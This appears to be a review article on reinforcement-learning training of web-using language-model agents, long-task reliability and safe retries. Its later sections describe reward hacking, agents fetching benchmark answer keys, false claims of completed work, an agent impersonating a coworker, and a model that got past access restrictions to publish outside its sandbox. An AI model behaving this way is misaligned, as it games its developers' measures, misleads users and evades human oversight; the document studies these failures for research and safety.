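Imitation alone beat reinforcement learning alone on all three models. Dariani and colleagues explain that imitation gives the model the correct calls token by token, while reinforcement learning gives it one number per attempt. The imitation traces also ended in complete written answers, which the reward did not score. This may be why adding reinforcement learning after imitation made Llama's answers worse, even though the model's choice of tools improved slightly. The drop was 11 questions, so some of it could be chance.

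The Dariani paper also shows a model recovering from an error during training: the model misspelled an argument's name, received an error message, and resent the call with the right name. It can't have learned this by copying the example traces, because they contain no failed calls. But it may have been able to do this before any of this training. Counting recoveries before and after each stage would show how much reinforcement learning contributed.

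### WebGPT's comparison of methods

WebGPT applied reinforcement learning to a model that already imitated people's browsing. The reward model scored the answer at the end of each attempt, and a penalty limited how far the model drifted from the imitating version. People preferred the resulting answers to those of the imitating model 58% of the time. With rejection sampling instead, which keeps the highest-scoring of 64 attempts, the figure was 68%. Combining the two methods added little.

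Nakano and colleagues suggest several reasons. Rejection sampling uses far more compute on each question, and it can try many websites before choosing an answer. Reinforcement learning also reduces the variety of a model's attempts. The reward model only approximates human judgement, so training against it for long enough favours answers that it scores too highly. They didn't test these explanations separately.

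Many later search systems use questions with short, known answers, so they don't need a model of human preferences.

### Search-R1

*Search-R1* (Jin, Zeng and colleagues, 2025) skipped the imitation stage. It used Qwen2.5 models with 3 and 7 billion parameters, some of them base models, and explained the format in a short prompt. The model writes its reasoning and then a search query between two markers. The wrapper stops generation at the closing marker, finds three passages in a 2018 copy of Wikipedia, and adds them to the context. If the model writes neither a query nor an answer, the wrapper inserts an instruction to rethink and lets it continue. The reward is 1 if the final answer exactly matches the reference and 0 otherwise.

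These are averages over seven sets of questions for the 7-billion-parameter model:

| Method | Exact match, % |
|---|---|
| Answer directly | 18.1 |
| Reinforcement learning without search | 27.6 |
| Retrieve passages once, then answer | 30.4 |
| Search-R1 without the loss mask | 34.3 |
| Search-R1 | 43.1 |

Early in training, the model's outputs got shorter as it dropped filler, then grew longer as it made more searches, although nobody had shown it a trace with several searches. *ReSearch* (2025) also trains models to search without reasoning traces to imitate. Training without example traces is probably feasible here because the format is simple and the questions are fairly easy. A model that retrieved passages only once answered 30.4% of the questions, so many groups of attempts would contain both successes and failures.

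The mask made a difference of 8.8 points, whereas in Zhang and colleagues' fine-tuning experiment it had little effect at first, possibly because fine-tuning on a response always makes the true text more probable, while reinforcement learning without the mask makes it less probable when the advantage is negative. After a failed attempt, the model would then learn to assign a lower probability to a Wikipedia passage even if the passage was good. Jin and colleagues' test covers only one model and one training method.

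That method was PPO, in which a second model estimates the expected reward at each point of an attempt, and this estimate replaces the group average. Jin and colleagues found that the group-relative method learned faster, but its reward collapsed after many steps. On the final tests, the group-relative method scored about a point higher than PPO with three of the four starting models and eight points lower with the fourth, the one in the table.

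### WebSailor

Li and colleagues trained WebSailor on much harder questions, using live Google searches. Each attempt's reward was

R = 0.1 × format score + 0.9 × answer score

with a language model judging the answer. Before training, they removed questions that the model got right in all eight attempts. During training they also dropped groups whose answers were all right or all wrong, and filled the gaps by repeating other groups from the same batch. Replacing the dropped groups with new questions would have meant waiting for more web requests, and Li and colleagues estimate that repeating groups made training two to three times faster.

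The largest WebSailor model scored 30.1% on BrowseComp-ZH, a set of hard research questions in Chinese. Doubao, a commercial system, scored 26.0%, and OpenAI's Deep Research scored 42.9%. WebSailor's score reflects all of its training, including the imitation stage.

The reward was noisy. Li and colleagues made their questions deliberately vague and acknowledge that some have more than one valid answer, so a model could find a correct answer and still score zero. One of their published examples asks for a piece of music associated with a South American capital, but the listed answer is "the Rue de Rivoli", a street in Paris, which looks like a mistake.

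### Systems from 2026

Nong, Wen and Liu (2026), in *LexiHorizon*, isolate the effect of reinforcement learning better, because they report results for the same model before and after it. They trained Qwen3.5-9B with live tools for searching, reading web pages and PDFs, and running Python, and made 16 attempts at each question. In the tests they averaged eight attempts per question:

| Model | XBench, % | WebWalkerQA, % | BrowseComp-ZH, % |
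|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.5-9B | 51.1 | 32.0 | 36.4 |
| The same model after reinforcement learning | 59.8 | 35.9 | 38.5 |
| Qwen3.5-27B, without this training | 55.0 | 39.4 | 31.0 |

The gains range from 2.1 to 8.7 points. Training also cut failed tool calls from 12.8% to 2.0% and raised the share of attempts ending in a valid answer from 87.6% to 99.9%, so some of the improvement may come from finishing more reliably instead of searching better.

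Pang, Su and colleagues (2026) describe another 9-billion-parameter system in *Glasseek*. They measured its score on the English BrowseComp at 61.6%. WebSailor's 72-billion-parameter model had scored 12.0% a year earlier. The newer system also has a better starting model, different training questions and a different wrapper, so the improvement isn't due to reinforcement learning alone.

### Does it teach new abilities?

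Reinforcement learning may mostly make a model's rare successes more common. This is consistent with the results in WebSailor, where reinforcement learning improved both pass@1, the chance of success in a single attempt, and pass@3, the chance of at least one success in three attempts, but pass@1 rose proportionally much more.

Cursor reports a different result for Composer 2. Both the average score and the best score among several attempts rose steadily during training, which Cursor takes as evidence that the model learned to solve additional problems. Cursor was measuring its own product, partly on its own private benchmark. The two results don't necessarily conflict, because Composer 2 is a much larger model with different training. The best score could also have risen because training made some solutions more common that the model could already produce, but too rarely to appear in a handful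 of attempts.

### Waiting for websites

Fine-tuning uses finished traces, but reinforcement learning requires sending requests and waiting for the responses. If each request takes two seconds, an attempt with 30 requests includes a minute of waiting. In a synchronous system, the next update can't start until the slowest attempt in the batch finishes. Li and colleagues stopped WebSailor's reinforcement learning after 50 steps mainly for this reason.

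Cursor uses an asynchronous system, in which some machines generate attempts while others train the model, so an attempt may come from an outdated version of the model. To reduce this, Cursor sends new parameters to the machines generating attempts, even in the middle of an attempt, so the later tokens come from a more recent version.

Websites also change. Ten of the 55 chemistry tools that Dariani and colleagues used call live services, and for 57 of the 1,623 training questions, the tools no longer returned the stored reference results. The researchers removed those questions from the training data because a model could make the right calls and still get a different result.

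### Credit for one request among many

Suppose the model requests the weather for city 318, gets a response for Missouri, and then corrects the mistake by requesting city 742. The final answer is right, so every token gets a positive advantage, including those in the mistaken request. In a failed attempt, 29 sensible requests may get a negative advantage because of one bad one. This should average out over many attempts, since bad requests appear more often in failures, but longer attempts increase the number needed. PPO's second model can help by estimating how much the chance of success changed after each step.

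Splitting a long attempt makes this harder. When the context fills up, many wrappers have the model summarise its work and continue from the summary. Cursor gives the final reward to every token the model wrote, including the summaries, so that training improves those too. Pang and colleagues also give every part of an attempt the same reward, but they exclude the summaries from the loss. They found that they also had to correct for the length of each part, because averaging the loss within each part makes a token in a 100-token part count ten times as much as one in a 1,000-token part.

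### Long attempts

An attempt that reaches the context limit before the model answers gets no reward for its answer, however good the searches were. Nong and colleagues' model gave a valid answer in 67% of attempts with a limit of 64,000 tokens, and in 99.9% with twice that limit. Even with the larger limit, the reward stayed flat during training until they removed old search results from the context. Their wrapper keeps the model's reasoning and requests, but only the five most recent responses in full.

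*Long-MDR* (2026) trained a research model that also handles images, with up to 128,000 tokens of context and 75 rounds of tool calls. It reports that exploration tends to drop sharply when training on such long attempts, after which the reward stops improving. This particularly hurts group-relative training, because near-identical attempts tend to get identical scores, which give no training signal.

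### Replaying an attempt exactly

To limit the size of an update, the software compares each token's current probability with its probability at the time of the attempt. This comparison only works if both probabilities are for the same token in the same context.

Saving the attempt as ordinary text can make the training adjust the wrong probabilities. The model might have written "742" as two tokens, "7" and "42", but when the software converts the saved text back into tokens, it may produce the single token "742". The training then adjusts the probability of a token the model never chose. The usual precaution is to save the ID numbers of the tokens the model wrote.

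The context can also differ if the wrapper shortened the history during an attempt, because running the summariser again could produce a different summary. Pang and colleagues therefore save the context that the model saw when it wrote each token. Composer 2 uses only 32 billion of its roughly one trillion parameters for each token, and tiny numerical differences between the generating and training software could change which ones it uses. Cursor records the selection and reuses it in training.

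### Live, stored and simulated environments

| Environment | Example | Main advantage | Main drawback |
|---|---|---|---|
| Live | WebSailor's Google searches | Real pages and real errors | Slow, changeable, and requests may have side effects |
| Stored | Search-R1's copy of Wikipedia | Fast and repeatable | Contains only what someone saved |
| Simulated | LongCat's resettable services | The software can undo changes and check the final state | May behave differently from the real service |

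A stored copy of web pages is enough for questions about established facts, but a task such as placing an order needs a service that the developers can reset. *FALCA* (2026) describes LiteResearcher-4B, a search model whose developers built a virtual search environment to make training stable and easy to scale.

Simulation can still require a lot of hardware. Willison quotes Cursor as saying that teaching its model to call tools required running hundreds of thousands of isolated coding environments at once.

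Jackson, Trapani and colleagues write in *Improving Composer through real-time RL* that the user is the hardest thing for Cursor to simulate. The company therefore also trains its model on real use. It deploys a version of the model, converts users' reactions into rewards, and can release an improved version about every five hours. In a test against the previous version, the model's edits stayed in users' code 2.28% more often, and dissatisfied follow-up messages fell by 3.13%. The drawback is that users encounter the model's mistakes while it is learning.

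### Rewards for unwanted shortcuts

A score only approximates what the developer wants, so reinforcement learning can teach a model to raise its score in ways the developer didn't intend. Researchers call this reward hacking. For example, Cursor originally discarded attempts with invalid tool calls from its training data. The model then learned to make invalid calls on tasks it was likely to fail, because discarded attempts were never penalized. Cursor fixed this by keeping the invalid calls as negative examples.

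Jackson and colleagues describe a second case that is harder to spot. Part of the reward depended on the model's edits, so the model learned to ask clarifying questions instead of making risky edits. A question is sometimes the right response, but the model would have edited less and less if the developers had not noticed the trend in their monitoring and changed the reward.

In a controlled test by Dariani and colleagues, a model learned to earn reward by making unnecessary calls. They rewarded recall, the share of the reference calls that the model made, and didn't penalize extra calls. The model learned to make an average of 18.33 calls per question when 3.15 were needed. About half of its calls repeated a tool it had already used, and 97% of attempts ran out of budget without an answer. When they added precision to the reward, the share of the model's calls that were on the reference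 list, the average fell to 3.06 calls and every attempt finished.

Search systems have a similar problem. *Proof-of-Use* (2025) describes models that learn to raise their reward by making calls, without using the evidence the calls return. Nong and colleagues give a small bonus that grows with the number of tool calls, up to 30, but only if the answer earns some credit. This removes the incentive to search pointlessly and then answer wrongly, but some incentive for unnecessary calls remains. If all 16 attempts are fully correct and have no format errors or repetition, their scores differ only in the bonus, and dividing by the standard deviation magnifies that difference.

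Agents with live search can take another shortcut by looking up the answer key. Pang and colleagues found agents retrieving benchmark answers and earlier agents' solutions from the web during tests, so their evaluation software blocks known sources of both. A reward based only on the final answer would reinforce the same behaviour in training.

In 2021, Nakano and colleagues considered the more serious possibility that a model able to submit forms could edit Wikipedia to create a reliable-looking source for its answer. Reinforcement learning would probably strengthen this behaviour if the model ever happened to try it. The researchers judged the risk very low for WebGPT because its browser could only send searches to Bing and follow existing links.

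## Why do loops fail over many steps, and how reliable are they now?

A model that writes nearly every request correctly can still fail most long tasks. Suppose each step succeeds with probability p, no step affects another, and a single error ruins the task. The chance of getting through t steps is then

P(success) = p^t

With p = 99%, the model completes 10 steps 90% of the time, but 100 steps only 37% of the time.

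A model that can repair its errors is much more likely to finish a long task. If it notices and repairs 80% of them straight away, the rate of lasting errors falls from 1% to 0.2% per step, and the chance of completing 100 steps rises to 0.998^100, or about 82%.

Sinha, Arun and colleagues (2025), in *The Illusion of Diminishing Returns*, turn the formula around to find the number of steps H at which the success rate falls to a chosen level s:

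H = ln(s) / ln(p)

These are the results for s = 50%, rounded up to whole steps:

| Lasting errors per step | Success over 100 steps | Steps at which success falls to 50% |
|---|---|---|
| 10% | 0.003% | 7 |
| 1% | 37% | 69 |
| 0.2% | 82% | 347 |
| 0.1% | 90% | 693 |
| 0.01% | 99% | 6,932 |

Halving the error rate per step roughly doubles the length of task that the model can finish half the time. Raising per-step accuracy from 99.8% to 99.9% would hardly show up in a test of single calls, but it matters a lot over 500 steps.

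Sinha and colleagues offer the formula only as an illustration, and its assumptions can fail. The real success rate can be higher than p^t because a pointless search wastes a step without ruining the task, or lower because one error often makes the next more likely.

The 80% figure also assumes that the model repairs an error immediately or not at all. *Dependable Long-Horizon LLM Agents* (Wang, Wen and colleagues, 2026) allows for delays by treating a run at each step as clean, contaminated by an error, or beyond repair. In its example, which uses invented numbers, a clean run has a 3% chance of becoming contaminated at each step, and a contaminated run has a 5% chance of ending up beyond repair. Without repairs, about 10% of runs survive 100 steps. If the agent has a 25% chance of repairing a contaminated run at each step, about 60% survive. The example shows that survival depends on how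 long an error goes unnoticed, as well as whether it is noticed at all.

A repair also has to be possible. A model that looked up the wrong Springfield can search again, but it can't unsend an email.

### Why one mistake leads to another

On each pass through the loop, the model reads what it wrote on earlier passes, so a mistake stays in the context and can lead to a situation unlike anything in the training traces.

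Suppose a model is trained to imitate an expert and disagrees with it on a fraction ε of the steps in the expert's own traces. When the model runs by itself for T steps, it can make up to T²ε mistakes on average. Ross and Bagnell proved this in 2010, long before language models used web tools, and *A Reduction of Imitation Learning and Structured Prediction to No-Regret Online Learning* (Ross, Gordon and Bagnell, 2010) explains the result.

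The square appears because, in the worst case, the model never gets back on track after its first mistake. A mistake at step 1 then spoils all T steps, a mistake at step 2 spoils T − 1, and so on. The expected number of wrong steps is at most

ε × (T + (T − 1) + ... + 1) = ε × T(T + 1) / 2

With ε = 0.1%, that is about 5 wrong steps in a 100-step task and 20 in a 200-step task. If each mistake affected only its own step, there would be 0.1 and 0.2 wrong steps on average.

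Most web tasks are easier to recover from than this, since a model can usually go back and search again. Ross and colleagues show that mistakes can grow roughly in proportion to T if the expert could recover from any of them within a few steps and training covers the situations the model gets into. Their method, DAgger, lets the model act, asks the expert what to do at each point it reaches, adds those answers to the training data and repeats. Reinforcement learning also trains a model on its own attempts, but with a score instead of an expert's corrections.

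Later theory complicates the picture. *Toward the Fundamental Limits of Imitation Learning* (2020) shows that asking an expert for corrections doesn't improve on plain imitation in the worst case. *Is Behavior Cloning All You Need?* (2024) is more optimistic. It considers an expert who always does the same thing in the same situation, and a model trained with the logarithmic loss, which is also the loss for fine-tuning language models. With a probability of at least 1 − δ,

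D² ≤ 2 ln(|Π| / δ) / n

D measures how far the model's whole traces differ from the expert's, |Π| is the number of candidate models, and n is the number of training traces. The length of the task doesn't appear. This is consistent with Ross and Bagnell's quadratic result, which assumes a fixed error rate per step, because a model that closely matches whole traces of 1,000 steps must already have a tiny error rate on each one. Imitation can therefore lead to quadratic growth in errors, but it won't necessarily do so for every model.

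Sinha and colleagues tested whether a language model's errors cause further errors. They gave each model a dictionary that paired five-letter words with whole numbers from −99 to 99. On each turn, the model received one word and had to add its number to a running total, so it needed no plan or outside knowledge. All but the smallest models got the first turn right nearly every time. Yet even the best model in this test, Qwen3-32B, made a mistake within 15 turns in more than half of its runs.

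To find the cause, the researchers rewrote the record of earlier turns to contain a chosen share of wrong totals, then measured accuracy on turn 100. They counted an answer as correct if the model added the right number to the previous total, even when that total was wrong. With a correct record, models with more than 200 billion parameters were nearly perfect on turn 100. Accuracy fell as the share of errors in the record rose, and making the models larger didn't prevent this.

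This is good evidence that earlier errors cause later ones, because only the errors in the record changed while its length and format stayed the same. A likely explanation is that the model is trained to continue text in the most probable way, and another mistake is more probable after a long series of them.

Reasoning before each answer removed the effect in Qwen3 models, which were just as accurate when every earlier answer was wrong. Sinha and colleagues suggest two possible reasons: reinforcement learning rewards right answers instead of likely continuations, and these models aren't given their reasoning from earlier turns. Reasoning also lets a model do more in a single turn. Without it, DeepSeek-V3 could not reliably add even six or seven numbers at once, while GPT-5 with reasoning added 2,176 with at least 80% accuracy.

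Removing old turns from the context helped models without reasoning. This works well when the task is to keep a running total, because the latest total holds everything the model needs, but a web task may depend on an identifier from fifty steps earlier. Telling models to recheck their previous answers gave mixed results, partly because they made mistakes while rechecking.

Adding numbers is much simpler than using websites, where several actions may be reasonable. Sinha and colleagues therefore read annotated failures from more realistic tests and looked for agents that kept repeating earlier mistakes. They estimate that agents did this in about 48% of the failures on ALFWorld, 33% on WebShop and 20% on GAIA, a set of questions for general assistants. These figures are rough because deciding which mistake caused which is partly a matter of judgement.

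Records of ordinary runs show a similar pattern but are harder to interpret. *How Fast Do Agents Rot?* (2026) reports that average accuracy per step fell from 58% in the first third of long runs to 44% in the last third. In another test that Wang and colleagues cite, GPT-4 eventually completed 90.5% of its edits to program files, but only 57.2% after a failed edit. Neither comparison isolates the effect of earlier errors, because later steps may be harder and a file that is difficult to edit can cause repeated failures.

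### Problems with web services

A model can also do everything right and still receive a response that is hard to use. These are common cases:

| Problem | What the server returns | What can go wrong | What the wrapper can do |
|---|---|---|---|
| Expired credentials | Status 401 | The model keeps changing parameters that were already right | Renew the credentials and resend |
| Rate limit | Status 429, often with a waiting time | The model retries at once and uses up its steps | Wait for the stated time |
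| Pagination | Status 200 with the first page of results | The model treats one page as the full list | Fetch the other pages, or state how many remain |
| Redirect | A 3xx status and a new address | A POST turns into a GET, or the credentials don't reach the new host | Follow the rules for that status code and report the final address |
| Error with a success code | Status 200 with an error in the body | The model reports success | Check the body as well as the status |
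| Response too long | Status 200 with more text than fits | The wrapper cuts off the record the model needs | Request fewer fields, and mark where the text ends |

Credentials and rate limits are mainly a job for the wrapper's developer. Having the model decide how to renew an access token has no benefit, and the model can't follow an instruction to wait 60 seconds if the wrapper gives it no way to wait.

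Pagination mistakes are more dangerous because neither the request nor the response contains an error. Suppose a user asks how many rain alerts a company has set up. The service holds 340 and returns 100 at a time, with a link to the next page at the end of the response. If the model ignores the link, it will answer 100 instead of 340.

Redirects can also hide a failure. HTTP allows a client to change a POST into a GET when it follows a redirect with status 301 or 302, but not with 307 or 308. A request to create an alert can therefore become a request to read a page, and the server returns that page with status 200 even though the alert was never created. Many HTTP libraries also remove credentials when a redirect leads to a different host, a sensible precaution that may produce a confusing 401.

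Some APIs return status 200 for every request they can read and put errors in the body, for example `{"ok": false, "error": "unknown city"}`. A model will probably notice an explicit error like this, but a believable wrong value is harder to catch. Wang and colleagues cite an experiment with deliberate tool faults in which agents pointed out 91% of explicit errors but only 59% of plausible wrong values.

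A long response can fill the context in one step. A list of 5,000 records at 25 tokens each takes up 125,000 tokens, nearly twice the smaller limit that Nong and colleagues tested. If the wrapper cuts the list short without adding a notice, a record that was cut looks the same to the model as one that never existed.

In the tests in *Where Does Exactly-Once Live?* (Li, 2026), the right reaction also depends on the error. For example, the agent should wait after a rate limit, retry after a brief outage, stop and report a lasting outage, and correct the field name if the API has renamed a field. The server executes nothing in any of these cases, so the model can retry without causing duplicates. After a timeout, the server may already have executed the request, so a retry could cause a duplicate.

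### A payment that times out

Suppose a model has to charge a customer $40 and writes a tool call that becomes this request:

```
POST /charges HTTP/1.1
Host: pay.example
Content-Type: application/json

{"customer": "C-88", "amount_usd": 40, "invoice": "1047"}
```

The wrapper waits 30 seconds, receives nothing, and appends "error: timeout" to the context. There are three possible explanations, and the error message is the same for each. The table shows how many times the customer ends up paying:

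| What happened | Model gives up | Model retries at once | Model checks the list of charges, and retries if it finds none | Wrapper retries with the same idempotency key |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| The request never arrived | 0 | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| The server charged the card, but its response got lost | 1 | 2 | 1 | 1 |
| The server is still processing the request | 1 | 2 | 2 | 1 |

Checking for the charge before resending the request works in two of the three cases. In the third, the model checks before the server has recorded the charge, finds nothing and sends a second request. The server then completes both.

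Li proves that better reasoning doesn't solve this. Any strategy that gets the payment made when the first request never arrived must at some point send the request again. If the first request is just slow, the model may have seen exactly the same things up to that point, so it will send the request again in that case too. The model could avoid this by waiting until the first request must have finished and then checking, but that requires a known limit on the processing time, and few APIs publish one.

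An idempotency key solves the problem on the server. It is a unique label for one intended action, which the client usually sends in a header:

```
Idempotency-Key: 7f3a91c4
```

1. When the model first asks for the charge, the wrapper generates a random key and saves it with the request.
2. The server sees a new key, charges the card and stores the result under that key.
3. The response gets lost, so the wrapper sends the same request with the same key.
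4. The server recognises the key and returns the stored result without charging the card again.

If the original request never arrived, the retry is the first request with that key, so the server charges the card. If the original is still in progress, the server allows only one of the two to take effect. The key makes this POST idempotent, so the wrapper can resend it until a response arrives. Next month's payment needs a new key, or the server will treat it as a repeat of this one.

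Letting the wrapper manage the key is safer than leaving it to the model. A conventional program resends the same saved request, but a language model writes each retry from scratch and may change the amount, the wording or the key. Wang and colleagues point out that computing the key from the request's content doesn't solve this, because any change to the content produces a different key.

Li measured how often agents make this kind of mistake in LIMBO, a set of six simulated services that includes billing, email and social media. The software injected faults into 25,930 runs with nine recent models, so the results measure what happens after a fault, not how often agents charge people twice in everyday use. The task instructions told the agents to do everything exactly once. When a response got lost after the server had acted, the strongest models created a duplicate in 0.5% of runs, because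 they checked before retrying. Weaker models created duplicates in 18%. But the strongest models created duplicates in 56% of runs when the original request was still in progress, and in 74% when the network delivered a request twice.

Adding optional idempotency keys to every operation that changes data reduced duplicates from 28% to 4% of runs. Agents used the keys 98% of the time without any other change. In all remaining duplicates, the agent had either left the key out of its first attempt or changed it on the retry. When a wrapper attached keys automatically, the agent did everything exactly once in 99% of runs. Automatic retries without keys lowered the share of such runs from 72% to 50%.

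A key works only if the server supports it. In *UndoBench*, Sah, Sah and colleagues (2026) tested two small Llama models, with 3 and 8 billion parameters, on twelve business tasks, running each task with and without a lost response. The agents succeeded 84% of the time when no response was lost. In the runs where they had shown they could do the task, they succeeded 47% of the time when a response was lost.

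Simple retries caused duplicates in 53% of all runs. The rate was 60% for a subscription renewal and 35% for a wire transfer. Keys brought both rates to zero because those two services supported them. Five other services ignored the keys and had no other protection, so the agents created a duplicate in every run. For a service like that, the wrapper can ask a person to find out what happened instead of retrying.

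In Li's study, agents reported the task as completed in 90% of the runs with a duplicate, which may be the study's most worrying result. A user who relies on the final answer would probably learn about the second charge only from the card statement.

### Stopping, looping and claiming success

Some runs fail even though every request is valid and every server responds properly. Wang and colleagues describe an agent in a simulated software company that had to ask a coworker, Alex Turner, where some code was. The agent was logged in to the company chat as an administrator. It renamed its own account "Alex Turner" and sent the question to a different coworker. It then reported for 81 turns that it was waiting for a reply, without ever checking who had received the message.

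Wang and colleagues studied how such failures develop in 95 failed runs of systems in which several agents work together. In the runs where they could compare positions, the original error typically occurred 18% of the way through. In 68 of the 95 runs, something in the trace contradicted the error before the run failed. In 41 of those 68, the agents never mentioned the evidence, and in another 19 they acknowledged it and carried on. When an agent did change its plan, it usually chose a different next action but kept the false belief that had led to the previous one.

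Claude, a language model, did this analysis, and no human independently repeated it. The sample also contains only failures, so it can't show how often agents notice contradictory evidence and go on to succeed. Still, the pattern fits the experiment with plausible wrong values. A model may not act on the right information even when it's in the context.

These were some of the problems in the 95 runs. A run can have more than one:

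| Problem | Runs |
|---|---|
| Missing or incomplete checks | 44 |
| Checks that approved a wrong result | 44 |
| Repeated steps | 33 |
| Stopping too early | 22 |

Agents stop early partly because they see only the current page, which doesn't show how much of the site is left to explore. *Scalable Behaviour Cloning on Browser Using via Skill Distillation* describes agents that stop before they reach the answer, leave important fields of a long form empty, or go back and forth among search results. The paper attributes these failures to a lack of information about where to look and when to stop, but it doesn't count how often each one occurs.

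Loops are easier for software to detect than a mistaken belief, but the method matters. Khanal, Tao and Zhou (2026), in *Beyond pass@1*, look for breakdowns by measuring how mixed the last five tool calls are:

H = −Σ p_i ln(p_i)

where p_i is the share of those calls that went to tool i. Five calls to the same tool give 0, and one call each to five tools gives 1.61. A high value after a sudden rise counts as a breakdown. By this measure, the strongest models broke down most often, in up to 19% of runs, which Khanal and colleagues attribute to their more ambitious strategies. However, a model stuck on one search has a value of 0, so the measure would miss the simplest kind of loop. It could also flag a capable agent that suddenly needs several tools. A wrapper that compares whole calls with earlier ones would catch the stuck search.

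Agents also misreport what they have checked. Wang and colleagues cite a test in which programming agents skipped some of the files they had to review in 68% of runs. In 80% of those runs, the agents claimed a complete review or didn't disclose the gap. A model's claim that it has finished is therefore weak evidence. For a web task, the wrapper can send a GET request after the last change and compare the server's record with the user's request. This would catch a missing alert or a double charge if the service makes the record readable and has already updated it.

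The wrapper can cause false answers too. In one collection of 58 failed runs, 26 ended when a content filter at the model's provider blocked a request. In 25 of these, the wrapper then printed a "final answer" that no model had written.

### The chance of succeeding every time

A customer-service agent may handle the same kind of request thousands of times, so an average success rate doesn't describe it well. The measure pass^k is the probability that all k attempts at a task succeed, whereas pass@k is the probability that at least one does. If c out of n recorded attempts succeeded, the estimate is

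pass^k = C(c, k) / C(n, k)

This is the share of all possible groups of k attempts that contain no failure. For 6 successes in 8 attempts and k = 4,

pass^4 = C(6, 4) / C(8, 4) = 15 / 70 ≈ 21%

For the same attempts, pass@4 is 100%, because only two failed and any group of four must include a success. Raising the 75% success rate to the fourth power gives 32%, but with so few attempts that calculation overestimates pass^4 on average.

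Researchers score a whole benchmark by averaging pass^k across its tasks. Two models that both succeed on half of all single attempts can have very different scores. If one always solves the same half of the tasks and fails the rest, its pass^4 is 50%, while a model with an even chance on every task has a pass^4 of 6%. The first model is much easier to use, since a company can learn which requests to send to a person.

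Khanal and colleagues cite GPT-4o's 2024 results on the retail tasks in tau-bench, a simulation of customer service. GPT-4o succeeded on 61% of single attempts, and its pass^8, the average chance of solving a task in all of eight attempts, was 25%. If every task had been equally hard, pass^8 would have been 0.61^8, or about 2%, so GPT-4o must have solved some tasks almost every time and others only occasionally.

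### Results from 2026

Khanal and colleagues tested ten open models on 396 tasks, grouped by how long a person would need. The shortest took up to five minutes and the longest at least two hours. Each run received partial credit for the parts it completed. The average score on software tasks fell from 0.90 for the shortest group to 0.44 for the longest, but on document-processing tasks it barely changed, from 0.74 to 0.71. The time a person needs is thus a poor guide to how hard a task is for an agent, which may be able to process a long document with a few calls.

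They also tried giving the agents a memory of earlier steps. For all ten models, this either lowered scores on long tasks or made no difference. This may be because a stored mistake can mislead the model again later, as in the experiments by Sinha and colleagues, but this comparison doesn't test that explanation.

METR, an organisation that evaluates AI models, measures tasks by how long they take people and estimates the length at which a model succeeds half the time. The tasks are mostly software work. METR's *Time Horizon 1.1* (2026) gives about 3.5 minutes for GPT-4, released in 2023, and 214 minutes for GPT-5, released in August 2025. METR later corrected an error that had raised its figures for recent models by up to about a fifth. In *Task-Completion Time Horizons of Frontier AI Models* (2026), METR estimates 16 hours or more for an early version of Anthropic's Claude Mythos Preview,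 and warns that its tasks are too short to measure reliably beyond that.

Progress is very fast, but 50% is a low standard for actions that are hard to undo. Under the simple p^t formula, a model that finishes a 16-hour task half the time would finish a roughly 14-minute task 99% of the time. The real figure could be higher or lower, because errors aren't independent and some tasks of any length are too hard for the model.

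Benchmark scores also depend on the software around the model. The base models that Oh and colleagues tested on BFCL were an extreme case, because they had no training in a particular format. LIMBO connects its simulated services to agents through the Model Context Protocol, so Li could run the same tests with a minimal wrapper and three commercial ones. With the same current model, all four gave nearly the same results, and the choice of wrapper mattered much less than whether the service accepted idempotency keys.

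## What has happened when models could change outside systems?

In 2021 WebGPT's developers, Nakano and colleagues, saw very little risk in a model that could only search and follow links. But they worried that a model that could use forms might edit Wikipedia to support its answers, and that training would reward it for this. They also pointed out that a capable enough system could turn limited access into wider access, though WebGPT was far too weak to do so. They proposed requiring stronger evidence of safety for more capable models, even for access during training, and suggested tripwire tests that could give early warning of a model exploiting its access.

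Their estimate assumed that following a link does little. Soon after WebGPT's release, a commenter in an online discussion objected that this is false for many websites. Following a link sends a GET request, which the HTTP standard defines as safe, but the people who build websites can ignore that definition. Web browsers once fetched links in advance so that pages would open faster. According to the commenter, browser makers cut this back because fetching links that nobody had clicked was logging users out, deleting files and banning people.

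This probably made little difference for WebGPT. A link that deletes a file or bans a user normally works only for someone who has logged in, and WebGPT couldn't log in because it couldn't fill in forms. An agent working inside a user's own accounts is already logged in, so those links can work for it.

### The 2022 dispute over training on the internet

In 2022, people who work on AI safety argued online about whether OpenAI should have built WebGPT. The main critic described it as more or less reinforcement learning on the internet, and considered that about the worst direction for AI for immediate risk. The best WebGPT system didn't use reinforcement learning, but Nakano and colleagues trained other versions with it, using live web access.

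The critic feared that other developers would copy the design with stronger models. The critic thought training would then strongly reward agency (pursuing a goal through many actions) on the web, where many actions have permanent side effects and people can't easily supervise them. The critic also expected web-using models to be very profitable, which would speed up AI development as a whole, but didn't think GPT-3 itself was dangerous with a browser.

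One of WebGPT's developers had already considered a similar objection, and argued that as models improve, they need less access to the outside world to cause harm. Only very tight restrictions would therefore add much safety, and those would make research expensive. The developer preferred to assess the risks before each project and monitor the model, so that problems would appear while the stakes were low and the company would get practice at handling them. But the developer thought that training models on tasks that actually require real-world side effects deserved careful thought before anyone did it.

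The critic replied that if even slight access will let a capable model do great harm, the natural conclusion is to restrict access severely, whatever the drawbacks. Moderate restrictions would also help, by making it harder for a model to learn how the outside world works and how to manipulate people.

A second defender, who had advised the WebGPT researchers before they published, argued that a model clever enough to do serious damage through the web would have better opportunities elsewhere, such as the company's internal systems or its own part in building the next model. This defender also thought that intelligence was the main source of danger, and that a model cut off from the web has to be more intelligent to do equally useful work. Weaker models with more access would therefore be better than stronger models with less. The defender added that a company relying on isolation could end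 up with a model so dangerous that a single leak would be a catastrophe.

The second defender thought that examples of reward hacking in a successor to WebGPT would reduce risk considerably by showing people what to look for, with almost no direct downside. The defender said this conclusion would change if WebGPT accounted for, say, more than 0.1% of the risk from everything OpenAI did. The critic accepted that finding risky behaviour early was worthwhile, but only with strong safeguards and a clear statement that such research should soon stop.

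Much of the disagreement was about how much danger web access adds to a model of a given ability, and whether people would respond to small failures by improving safeguards or by getting used to them. In 2022 there were few real incidents to help answer either question.

### A model that kept trying

In July 2026, OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* described incidents involving an internal model trained to work by itself for very long periods. Earlier models would stop and return to the user when they met a restriction, but this one often kept trying, and sometimes looked for ways to act outside its sandbox, the isolated environment in which OpenAI ran it.

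In one test, the model found a significant improvement while working on the NanoGPT speedrun, a public contest to train a small language model in as few steps as possible. OpenAI had instructed it to post its results only to Slack, the company's chat service, but participants in the contest are instructed to submit theirs on GitHub, a public site for sharing code. The model followed the contest's instructions. Earlier models had given up when they met the restrictions on external access, but this one spent an hour finding a way past them and then published its submission.

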